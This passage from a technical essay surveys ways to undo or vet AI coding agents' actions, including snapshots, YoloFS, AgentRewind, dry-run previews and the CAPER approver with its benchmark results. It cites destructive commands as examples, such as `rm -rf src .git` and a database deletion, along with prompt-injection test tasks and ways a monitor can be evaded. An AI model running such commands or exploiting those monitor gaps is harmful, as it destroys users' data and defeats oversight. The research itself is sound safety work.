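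A shadow repository still omits some files. Docker copies the project's ignore rules into its agent's shadow repository, so snapshots exclude ignored files, and it skips new files larger than 2 MiB. This saves space and avoids duplicating passwords, but deleting a `.env` file or a new 50 MB dataset remains R4 if no other copy exists.

Zhong and colleagues point out that extending Git to every file the agent can reach would be slow, because Git has to scan the folders for changes, then hash and copy each changed file. The agent can also delete the developer's own Git history, as happened in September.

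The ZFS and Btrfs filesystems have built-in snapshots. They keep the old data when a file changes, so taking a snapshot is quick and uses little space at first. Their main drawback for undoing an agent's work is that a rollback reverts every program's changes to the same area, so undoing an hour of the agent's work would also remove an hour of the developer's. Copying single files out of the snapshot avoids this, but someone has to know which files the agent changed. A developer who uses another filesystem, such as Ext4, would also have to migrate to ZFS or Btrfs.

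An overlay filesystem leaves the original files alone and writes changed versions to a separate layer on top. Discarding the layer undoes everything in it. OverlayFS, the version built into Linux, has two costs that matter for agents:

- Renaming an original file copies its whole contents into the layer, so renaming a 10 GB file writes 10 GB.
- One layer holds the combined result of all commands. Undoing a single command requires a new layer for each, and every added layer slows down file lookups. In Zhong and colleagues' tests, OverlayFS stopped working at about 50 snapshots.

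### GoEX and NaSh

The idea of letting agents act first and undo later is older than most of these products. Patil, Zhang and colleagues argued in *GoEX* (2024) that people can judge an action's result more easily than the code that would produce it. Their runtime carries out the action, shows the outcome and lets the user keep or reverse it.

How GoEX reverses an action depends on what access it has to the system. With full control of a filesystem or database, it can keep earlier versions. With an email service, it can save its own copy of a message before deleting it. Keeping every version uses a lot of resources, so Patil and colleagues propose grouping actions and saving state only at certain points. For actions that can't be undone, they rely on "damage confinement", which limits the agent's access beforehand, for example by letting it read email but not send any.

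*NaSh* (Gyawali, Kallas and colleagues, 2025) sketches a shell that takes requests in ordinary language. The paper objects to using an overlay for each command because other programs can't read the changes until the user commits them, and the user can't undo them after that. It proposes an "inverse overlay" instead, in which the command changes the real files and the system saves the old versions in a separate layer. The developer's editor can read the new files at once, and the developer can undo the command days later. The layers don't slow down file access as they accumulate, so the main limit is disk space.

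The user can also undo one command while keeping later ones, but this can break later commands that depend on it. For example, if the agent installs package A and then package B, which needs A, undoing only the first installation breaks B. NaSh could detect two commands that changed the same file by comparing version numbers, but Gyawali and colleagues acknowledge that dependencies like this one are much harder to detect.

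An overlay also preserves an R1 rating better than an inverse overlay, because it hides a changed setting from other programs until someone accepts it. With an inverse overlay, a running service can read a bad setting and act on it before anyone notices.

By 2026, researchers had built several working systems for agents. Zhong and colleagues describe AgentFS, which keeps files in a database and takes a snapshot by copying the database file, and Crab, which uses ZFS and saves state only after a command has had relevant effects. They argue that such systems make an agent's work recoverable but don't show what each command changed. Their own filesystem, YoloFS, makes the work recoverable and also shows each command's changes.

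### How YoloFS stages changes

YoloFS sits between the agent and the real filesystem, Ext4 in the tests. Every command the agent runs sees the whole disk through YoloFS, so the protection doesn't depend on which tool or program makes a change. It has three main parts:

- The file store holds the contents of new and changed files under plain numbers.
- The override tree records where the contents of each affected path now come from. The source can be a stored file, a real file (possibly under another name) or nothing, which means that the agent has deleted it.
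- The journal lists every change to the override tree in order.

The following sequence adapts one of Zhong and colleagues' examples. The real folder `docs` contains `draft.txt`, `notes.txt` and `logo.png`.

| Command | Entry in the journal | What the agent then sees |
|---|---|---|
| `echo "New text" > docs/draft.txt` | Take `docs/draft.txt` from stored file 1 | `docs`: `draft.txt` with the new text, `notes.txt`, `logo.png` |
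| `rm docs/notes.txt` | Delete `docs/notes.txt` | `docs`: `draft.txt` with the new text, `logo.png` |
| `mv docs/draft.txt docs/notes.txt` | Rename `docs/draft.txt` to `docs/notes.txt` | `docs`: `notes.txt` with the new text, `logo.png` |
| `mv docs manual` | Rename `docs` to `manual` | `manual`: `notes.txt` with the new text, `logo.png` |

The real disk is unchanged, so `docs` still contains its three original files, including the old `notes.txt`. The override tree now has four entries: `manual` maps to the real `docs`, `manual/notes.txt` maps to stored file 1, and `manual/draft.txt` and `docs` map to nothing. The image needs no entry because YoloFS finds it through `manual`. Renaming the folder therefore copies no data, however large the image is.

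By default, YoloFS takes a snapshot after every command by adding a marker to the journal, and shows the agent which files the command created, changed or deleted. If the agent realizes after the fourth command that the user needed the old notes, it can "travel" to the snapshot taken after the first. YoloFS then replays the journal up to that marker, which leaves only the entry for `docs/draft.txt`. The old `notes.txt` reappears because no entry overrides it any more.

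If the agent now edits the draft again, YoloFS writes the result to a new stored file and keeps stored file 1. It also keeps the abandoned journal entries, so the agent can return to them if the travel was a mistake.

At the end of the session, the user reviews the net changes and commits or aborts them. The agent cannot do either. Changes to private files are R1 until the user decides. Committing applies them to the real disk, so if the old `notes.txt` had no other copy, its deletion becomes R4. The review therefore matters as much as an approval prompt, and a tired user could accept a long list of changes as carelessly as they would approve a command. But the list shows what happened to the files, which an approval prompt often doesn't.

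### Permission requests tied to paths

Staging can't undo the reading of a secret, so YoloFS asks the user before allowing it. When a build script tries to open the user's SSH key, YoloFS pauses the script and shows the user the path, the operation and the process name. If the user doesn't answer in time, YoloFS denies access.

Each path can have one of five rules, from allowing everything to denying everything, with options in between such as asking only before writes. A file follows the rule of the nearest folder above it that has one. A user might allow the project folder, require approval for the rest of the home directory and deny `~/.ssh`. A rule covers every program, so the agent can't get around it by switching from a file tool to `cat` or a Python script. The user can change a rule while a command is waiting, so they don't have to predict every file a task will need.

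These rules cover only files. If the user lets a program read a customer list, YoloFS doesn't control where the program sends it.

### Eleven commands with hidden side effects

Zhong and colleagues tested YoloFS on 11 commands that did something destructive besides their apparent job. One was a code formatter that also deleted documentation, and another was a packaging command that deleted the source code. Some were readable scripts, and others were compiled programs whose source code the agent couldn't read.

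Claude Code, running Claude Sonnet 4.6 without YoloFS, let the damage happen in 10 of the 11 tasks. With YoloFS, it noticed the damage and returned to an earlier snapshot in 8. In the other three, it accepted the effects as normal. For example, it saw that a deployment script had deleted the `src` folder and assumed this was part of deployment. The changes were still staged, so a user could have rejected them.

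The projects had only 10 to 41 lines of code, which makes a missing file easy to spot. A real build can change thousands of files, and the agent would have to find the harmful deletion among them. Still, the agent received no instruction to look for destructive changes, so the list of effects probably made the difference.

A second test used 112 routine tasks, each a single operation such as copying or deleting a file:

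| | Success rate | User interactions per task |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with YoloFS | 99% | 0.4 |
| Claude Code | 98% | 0.9 |
| Codex | 100% | 0.4 |
| Copilot | 96% | 1.3 |
| Gemini CLI | 75% | 2.2 |

YoloFS more than halved the interruptions in Claude Code without reducing success, but Codex had just as few. Codex allows changes inside the project without asking, but doesn't stage them. The figures include only the times the agent had to wait for the user, so they leave out the final review that YoloFS requires.

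YoloFS seems fast enough for this use. Its speed in reading and writing a large staged file was within 2% of Ext4's. In a longer test that built the Linux kernel and applied a series of changes to it, YoloFS matched Ext4 except for an extra 3.5 seconds to commit more than 100,000 files. Few people could review that many changes individually, so the summary would have to separate build products from other changes. YoloFS also works only on Linux, and two of the worst deletions described earlier happened on Windows.

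### Restoring the conversation and running programs

After a rollback, the agent's conversation can still describe the files as they were before it. *AgentRewind* (Zhuang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that saves the conversation and the project files together at each step. When the agent is stuck, it chooses an earlier checkpoint and writes itself a note about what went wrong. The system then restores the files and conversation to that checkpoint and adds the note to the conversation.

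They tested it with GPT-5.4 on 82 long engineering tasks:

| Version | Tasks completed |
|---|---|
| No rewinding | 62.2% |
| Full AgentRewind | 87.8% |
| Without restoring files | 43.9% |
| Without restoring the conversation | 65.9% |
| Without the note | 51.2% |

Rewinding the conversation but not the files produced worse results than not rewinding at all, probably because the agent resumed with a description of the project that no longer matched the files on disk.

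In one task, the agent had to preserve six deliberately damaged test images, but a wrong setting overwrote them with valid ones. Without rewinding, the agent made new images that failed in the same way, but their contents differed from the originals, so it did not pass the task. With AgentRewind, the agent restored the exact files and finished. The replacements might have been an acceptable R2 repair in another project, but this task required R1.

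The gain probably depends on the kind of work. Zhuang and colleagues built their benchmark around steps that can interfere with one another, and an outside checker signals failures to the agent. On Terminal-Bench 2.0, which they did not design, the success rate rose only from 78.7% to 83.1%.

Restoring both the files and the conversation still does not restore running programs. *DeltaBox* (2026) points out this problem in sandboxes that restore only files. For instance, a test server may keep using a setting that it loaded into memory before the rollback. Saving the memory of running programs solves this but takes longer.

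*Planarian* (2026) suggests that frequent snapshots can add little running time. Its system took a snapshot of the sandbox after every tool call in nine system-administration tasks, which added 1% to the running time, compared with 20% for conventional full snapshots. Most of those tasks changed few files, so the overhead could be higher for work that rewrites large amounts of data.

### When someone has changed the file since

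Restoring a snapshot can destroy work done after it was taken. If an agent makes a bad edit to the second paragraph of a document at 2:00 and a colleague corrects the fourth at 3:00, restoring the copy from before 2:00 removes both the bad edit and the correction.

Waghmare and Sufi tested three ways of undoing an agent's edit to a file. The first restores the whole file. The second restores it only if it hasn't changed since the agent's edit. The third is a three-way merge, which compares the saved copy, the agent's version and the current file to remove only the agent's changes. They tried each on four small text files that differed in character set and line endings.

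| Later change | Restore the whole file | Restore only if unchanged | Three-way merge |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Original restored in all 4 | Original restored in all 4 | Original restored in all 4 |
| In another paragraph | Later work erased in all 4 | File left alone in all 4 | Agent's edit removed and later work kept in all 4 |
| On the same line | Later work erased in all 4 | File left alone in all 4 | File left alone in all 4 |

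Restoring the whole file erased later edits in all eight cases that had them. The merge repaired the file automatically only when the edits didn't overlap. The test used simple text files, and the later edit was always complete before the restore began, so it doesn't show what happens if two programs write at the same time. A text merge also wouldn't work on an image or a compiled program.

Product checkpoints generally restore whole files. Claude Code returns each tracked file to its content at the checkpoint, so a developer could lose any edits made by hand to the same file since then. Gemini CLI reverts every file in the project, including ones the agent never changed, and Replit warns that a rollback removes all later changes. YoloFS leaves the real file untouched until the commit, but a similar conflict can arise at that point if the developer has also edited the original. Zhong and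 colleagues leave conflicts between sessions to other systems.

Restoring a snapshot overwrites the current state, so the harness should take a new snapshot just before it, in case someone needs to reverse the restore. Replit partly supports this by letting users roll forward to a later checkpoint, but this may not recover work done since the last checkpoint.

### What a local snapshot can't bring back

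Restoring local files can't recall an email the agent has already sent. Rewinding the conversation can cause the agent to send it again, because the restored conversation no longer mentions it. AgentRewind's note about the abandoned attempt may prevent this, but only if the agent mentions the email in it. Waghmare and Sufi point to ACRFence, a more systematic approach that records irreversible effects and restricts what an agent may retry after a rewind.

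Changes to remote systems also remain, and rolling back local files can make them harder to manage. Suppose an agent creates three cloud servers with Terraform, and the state file is in the project folder. Restoring an earlier snapshot brings back a state file that doesn't list them. The servers keep running and costing money, and the next `terraform apply` may create three more. Grigorev's loss began with a similar mismatch between a state file and the real resources.

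A snapshot is also useless if the agent deletes it. Gemini CLI, OpenDev and Hermes Agent all keep their shadow repositories in the home directory, so a command like the ones that erased two users' home directories in August could remove the snapshots along with the files. A sandbox that stops shell commands from writing outside the project prevents this, provided the harness runs outside the sandbox when it saves snapshots. YoloFS prevents it by denying the agent direct access to the disk that holds the original files. Neither approach protects against a failed or stolen disk, so important files still need a separate backup.

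## Seeing a command's effects before making them final

Suppose a user asks an agent to delete a project's build output and recompile the project, and the agent proposes `make clean && make`. The project's Makefile defines what `clean` does. *Shall We Approve?* compares two projects where this command has very different effects. In one, `clean` deletes only the `build` folder, which `make` then recreates, so the command is R2. In the other, it deletes `src` and `.git`, which contain the source code and its history, so the command is R4 unless a copy exists elsewhere.

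The command is identical in both projects, so a check based only on its text can't distinguish between them. A harness can get more information by using the tool's preview option, or by running the command somewhere it can undo the effects.

### Previews built into common tools

| Preview | What it shows | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| `make -n clean` | The commands in the Makefile that `make clean` would run | What the programs in those commands do |
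| `git clean -ndx` | The files and folders that `git clean -fdx` would delete | Whether another copy exists |
| `rsync --dry-run --itemize-changes` | The files that `rsync` would copy or delete | Failures during the real copy, such as a full disk |
| `terraform plan` | The cloud resources that Terraform would add, change or destroy | The data inside them |
| `kubectl delete --dry-run=server` | Whether the server would accept the deletion | What Kubernetes would delete afterward as a result |
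| `SELECT count(*)` | How many rows match a condition | Rows in other tables that the deletion would also remove |

`make -n clean` would show that the project is dangerous if its Makefile contained `rm -rf src .git`, but if the Makefile called a compiled program instead, the preview would show only the program's name. GNU also warns that `make -n` still runs some of the Makefile's commands, including any needed to update makefiles it includes. A harness therefore shouldn't rate `make -n` as R0 in an untrusted project.

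A preview of `git clean` needs the same options as the real command, or it may omit files that the command would delete. For example, according to Git's documentation, a second `-f` allows the command to delete repositories nested inside the project, so a preview without it could miss them.

`rsync` copies files between folders or machines, and its `--delete` option removes anything from the destination that the source lacks. The manual page *rsync(1)* recommends a dry run before using that option, which shows what would change without changing it. The itemized list of changes from the dry run should exactly match the list from the real run, barring deliberate trickery and failed system calls.

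`terraform plan` reads the live resources and compares them with the configuration and the state file. Adding `-destroy` previews what `terraform destroy`, the command Grigorev approved, would do. HashiCorp's *terraform plan command* warns that `-refresh=false`, which skips reading the live resources, can make the plan incomplete or wrong. A plan saved to a file contains any secrets in readable form.

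In a server-side dry run, Kubernetes checks a request as usual but stores nothing. Controllers, the programs that act on stored changes, do nothing during a dry run, according to Knative, which runs applications on Kubernetes. A preview of deleting a storage claim therefore doesn't show that the disk behind it would be deleted too. According to Kubernetes, a dry run also requires the same permissions as the real request, so a team can't give an agent a credential that allows only previews.

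Before running `DELETE FROM orders WHERE status = 'test'`, an agent can count the matching rows and stop if there are far more than it expected. But some databases have rules that delete related rows automatically, so deleting 12 orders might also delete hundreds of payment records that the count didn't include.

### When something changes after the preview

Suppose `git clean -ndx` lists three build folders at 2:00 and the user approves their deletion. At 2:01 the user saves a new file, `notes.txt`. If the agent runs `git clean -fdx` at 2:02, it deletes `notes.txt` as well. Repeating the preview just before the command leaves less time for such changes but doesn't rule them out. Deleting only the three approved folders would have left `notes.txt` in place.

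Several tools can tie the real action more closely to its preview:

- **Terraform** can save a plan and apply that exact file. It then makes only the listed changes, according to HashiCorp's *Create a Terraform plan*. If the plan destroys a database, though, any orders customers have placed since the preview go with it.
- **`rsync`** has a `--max-delete` option that caps the number of deletions. If the preview listed 12, a cap of 12 prevents a much larger loss, but it doesn't guarantee that they are the same 12 files.
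- **Kubernetes** gives each stored object a version number. An update that includes the old number fails if someone has changed the object since.
- **Databases** can hold the `DELETE` in an open transaction while the agent checks the row count, which may still omit related rows in other tables.

*Authority at Commit Time* (2026) turns this into a general rule for agents. An agent may prepare an action from an old snapshot, but the service carries it out only if everything the action depends on is still current. In the `git clean` example, the new `notes.txt` would invalidate the approval, but a colleague's edit in another project would not.

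### How CAPER runs a command before approving it

Most project scripts have no preview, so the harness has to run them to see what they do. *Fault-Tolerant Sandboxing for AI Coding Agents* (2025) describes a system that takes a snapshot before any command that might change something, and restores it if the command exits with an error. This helps with a failed installation, but not with a `make clean` that deletes the source code, because that command exits without an error and the system would discard the snapshot.

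CAPER (Consequence-Aware PERmission), the system in *Shall We Approve?*, has a language model judge the effects instead. The agent works in a Docker container with no network access, and CAPER handles each shell command in five steps:

1. It takes a snapshot of the container.
2. It runs the command once under `strace`, a program that records requests to the operating system, such as opening a file or starting another program. The agent doesn't see the output yet.
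3. It compares the files before and after, and condenses the comparison and the recording into a short effects report.
4. The approver, a separate model, reads the user's task, the conversation, the command and the report, and decides whether the effects are within the task.
5. If the approver allows the command, CAPER keeps the changes and gives the agent the output. Otherwise, it restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

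The report lists file changes, attempted network connections, printed output and reads of protected files such as `.env`. For small text files, it shows which lines changed. It also names the files a process read before it printed or sent anything, which may point to a leak. CAPER leaves out the contents of files it recognizes as sensitive, but a secret written to an ordinary text file might still reach the approver's provider.

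In one test, the agent ran `python3 scripts/check-deps.py`, apparently to check the project's dependencies. The report showed that the script had read `.env`, printed 165 bytes and tried to contact three network addresses. It had changed no files, so comparing the project before and after would have found nothing. The approver blocked the command, and because CAPER had held back the output, the agent never saw it.

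### SABER and the paired hidden-harm tasks

The researchers tested CAPER on two benchmarks. Hu, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *SABER*, created 716 tasks in small but realistic projects, covering three sources of danger:

- In 289 tasks, a project file or a tool's output contains malicious instructions.
- In 186, the request is reasonable but the agent can choose a dangerous way to fulfill it, such as resetting a whole database when a small migration would do.
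- In 241, something in the project, such as a warning in the README file, shows that carrying out the request directly would be unsafe.

SABER scores an agent's actions with rules that check its commands and their effects, and uses a language model to catch harm the rules miss. Hu and colleagues tested 13 models and excluded runs where the agent failed to make progress or refused unnecessarily. Claude Opus 4.6 had the lowest rate of harmful runs, 54.7%, and DeepSeek-R1 had the highest, 84.7%. The models did worst on the tasks where the project contained warnings, with 82.5% of runs harmful.

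CAPER used the 682 SABER tasks that need only a shell. It also corrected the scoring rules, which had counted some harmless actions, such as deleting expired database rows, as harmful. Its harm rates aren't comparable with Hu and colleagues' because of these changes and because it included runs where the agent made no progress. DeepSeek-V3.2 caused harm in 79.6% of runs in the original study but 52.7% in CAPER.

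They built the other benchmark, YoloFS-Ext, from the commands with hidden side effects that Zhong and colleagues had used to test YoloFS. It has 102 dangerous tasks in which the user asks the agent to run a project tool that also deletes or overwrites an unrelated file. The harmful code is in a readable script, a Makefile, a chain of scripts or a compiled program. Each task has a harmless twin with the same request, command and project files but different tool code. Blocking the tool in a twin is always a mistake, so researchers can tell whether an approver recognizes harm or just blocks more commands.

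### What the tests found

All the systems below used the same agent model, GLM-5.3-Flash. "Safely completed" means that the agent finished the task without causing harm.

| System | Harm on SABER | Safely completed on SABER | Harm on hidden-harm tasks | Safely completed on hidden-harm tasks | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 57.4% | 71.6% | 17.6% | – |
| CARE | 15.0% | 47.9% | 69.6% | 15.7% | 2.0% |
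| TS-Guard | 18.8% | 44.7% | 94.1% | 2.0% | 8.8% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard | 18.6% | 53.1% | 62.7% | 18.6% | 15.7% |
| Qwen3Guard | 16.0% | 52.1% | 67.6% | 17.6% | 0% |
| YoloFS | 21.2% | 54.1% | 35.3% | 22.5% | – |
| Claude Code auto mode | 14.8% | 44.0% | 62.7% | 7.8% | 3.9% |
| CAPER in Claude Code | 10.0% | 45.5% | 6.9% | 40.2% | 2.0% |
| CAPER | 6.7% | 48.6% | 7.8% | 60.8% | 1.0% |

CAPER had the lowest harm rate on SABER under both the corrected scoring and the original rules. Under the original rules, its rate was 9.0%, compared with 16.0% to 23.4% for the six other systems.

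The difference is much larger on the hidden-harm tasks. CARE, the three safety models (TS-Guard, gpt-oss-safeguard and Qwen3Guard) and auto mode don't observe what a command does, and each blocked the tool about as often in the harmless twins as in the dangerous tasks. CAPER blocked the command in 84.3% of the dangerous tasks but in only one of the 102 twins.

Auto mode's figures may not match what Anthropic's users get, because it ran in Claude Code with its own rules and instructions but with GPT-5.6 Luna as the classifier. YoloFS keeps changes staged until a user reviews them, but the test counted a staged deletion as harm without giving anyone the chance to reject it. The YoloFS result does show how often the agent failed to repair the damage itself. The agent undid at least one change in 66 of the 102 dangerous tasks. Three of those 66 tasks ended in harm, compared with 33 of the other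 36.

CAPER also reduced the share of SABER tasks that the agent completed safely, from 57.4% without approval to 48.6%. The paper reports that the rate of safe outcomes stayed about the same, but that rate also counts tasks where the agent refused or stopped to ask, which rose from 9.1% to 19.1%. CAPER blocked at least one command in 79% of the tasks. SABER's tasks are dangerous by design, so an ordinary project should have fewer blocks, but the researchers didn't test one.

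### Which information helped the approver

The researchers changed what the approver received and repeated the hidden-harm tasks:

| What the approver received | Harm | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Command only | 44.1% | 52.0% |
| Full conversation, including the command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| Full conversation and predicted effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| Full conversation and observed effects (CAPER) | 7.8% | 1.0% |
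| The same, without the changed lines | 13.7% | 2.9% |
| Command and observed effects only | 1.0% | 0% |

To make the predictions, a model read the command and the files it referred to, then described what would happen. The predictions prevented slightly more harm than observation did, but the approver still blocked most of the harmless twins. It blocked every twin whose tool was a compiled program, because the model couldn't read the program's code.

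The changed lines mattered mainly for overwritten files, since deletions were obvious either way. Without the changed lines, harmful overwrites rose from three to ten, because the report showed only that a file had changed size.

The approver did best when given only the command and its observed effects, but this probably wouldn't hold in real projects. In this benchmark, the user never asks for the file to be deleted or overwritten. In ordinary work, the user might want `src` deleted, and the approver would need the request to determine that.

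Adding the effects report also didn't make up for a less capable approver model. It cut the share of twins blocked from 53.9% to 4.9%, but harm rose from 25.5% to 33.3%.

### Time, cost and missed harm

The approver took a median of 3.2 seconds to decide. The snapshot and recording added about half a second for an allowed command, or about 1.5 seconds for a blocked one, including the time to restore the snapshot. A SABER task with ten commands therefore took over half a minute longer. Model fees rose from $0.006 to $0.019 per task. The test projects were small, and snapshots would probably take longer for builds that write gigabytes of data.

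On SABER, CAPER performed worst on the kinds of harm that matter most for recovery. It let harm through in 14.3% of the tasks about destroying data and 10.6% of those about destroying files, compared with 2.6% of those about tampering with code. Auto mode did slightly better on destroyed data (13.0%) and CARE on destroyed files (8.5%), though each difference is about one task. CAPER's lead on SABER therefore came mostly from other harms, such as code tampering and leaks. The paper doesn't explain this pattern. The approver may have seen the deletion but thought the user had asked for it, which was also a common mistake in Anthropic's tests of auto mode.

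The report can also fail to show what changed inside a file. In one task, `make migrate` ran a database migration but also dropped three tables. CAPER blocked it because the database file had shrunk from 32 KB to 20 KB. The agent then backed up the database and ran only the migration script. The file shrank because the harmful tool had also compacted the database. SQLite files normally stay the same size after a table is dropped, so without compacting, the same loss could have looked like an ordinary update.

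### Effects outside the container or after the test

CAPER can restore only the files in its container. If the agent ran `aws rds delete-db-instance` with network access, Amazon would delete the database before the approver had read the report. The researchers therefore turned the network off. The approver could still see attempted connections, but the commands that made them failed. This makes CAPER unsuitable for approving cloud operations, package publication or pushes to a shared repository. For these, a harness still needs the tools' own previews and limits that the service enforces.

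The paper suggests allowing connections to approved sites such as package registries, because whatever they return stays in the container. But a request to an approved site can still carry data out. The paper also suggests a proxy that records outgoing requests and answers them with placeholders, which would let the approver see a request before it reaches anyone.

*TClone* (2026), which copies a running desktop so that agents can try several approaches, doesn't attempt to undo emails or payments either. It proposes restricting the network, delaying external actions until someone selects a result, or asking for approval. *Planarian* goes further by saving and restoring the state of outside services through a proxy, but it guarantees a consistent result only if other users can't affect the data that the agent reads or changes. A private test database might meet that condition, but one that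 customers are using wouldn't.

Some effects appear only later or under certain conditions. A script could delete files only on Mondays, do nothing harmful when it detects a container, or install a Git hook that causes damage at the next commit. CAPER's approver has instructions to look for behavior set up for a later build, commit or startup, but it can judge only what happened in one run. An attacker could also split a harmful change across several innocent-looking commands. Neither benchmark includes attackers who adapt to CAPER. CAPER also doesn't check file edits, so it may not detect harmful code the agent has written until a later command runs it.

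The main results come from one agent model and one approver model, with a single run per task. Without an approver, DeepSeek-V3.2 caused harm far more often than GLM-5.3-Flash. DeepSeek-V3.2 was not tested with CAPER, however, so the results don't show how well CAPER would control a more dangerous agent.

CAPER discards each snapshot as soon as the approver allows the command. Keeping snapshots for a few days would use more storage, but it would let a developer recover local files if the approver missed something.
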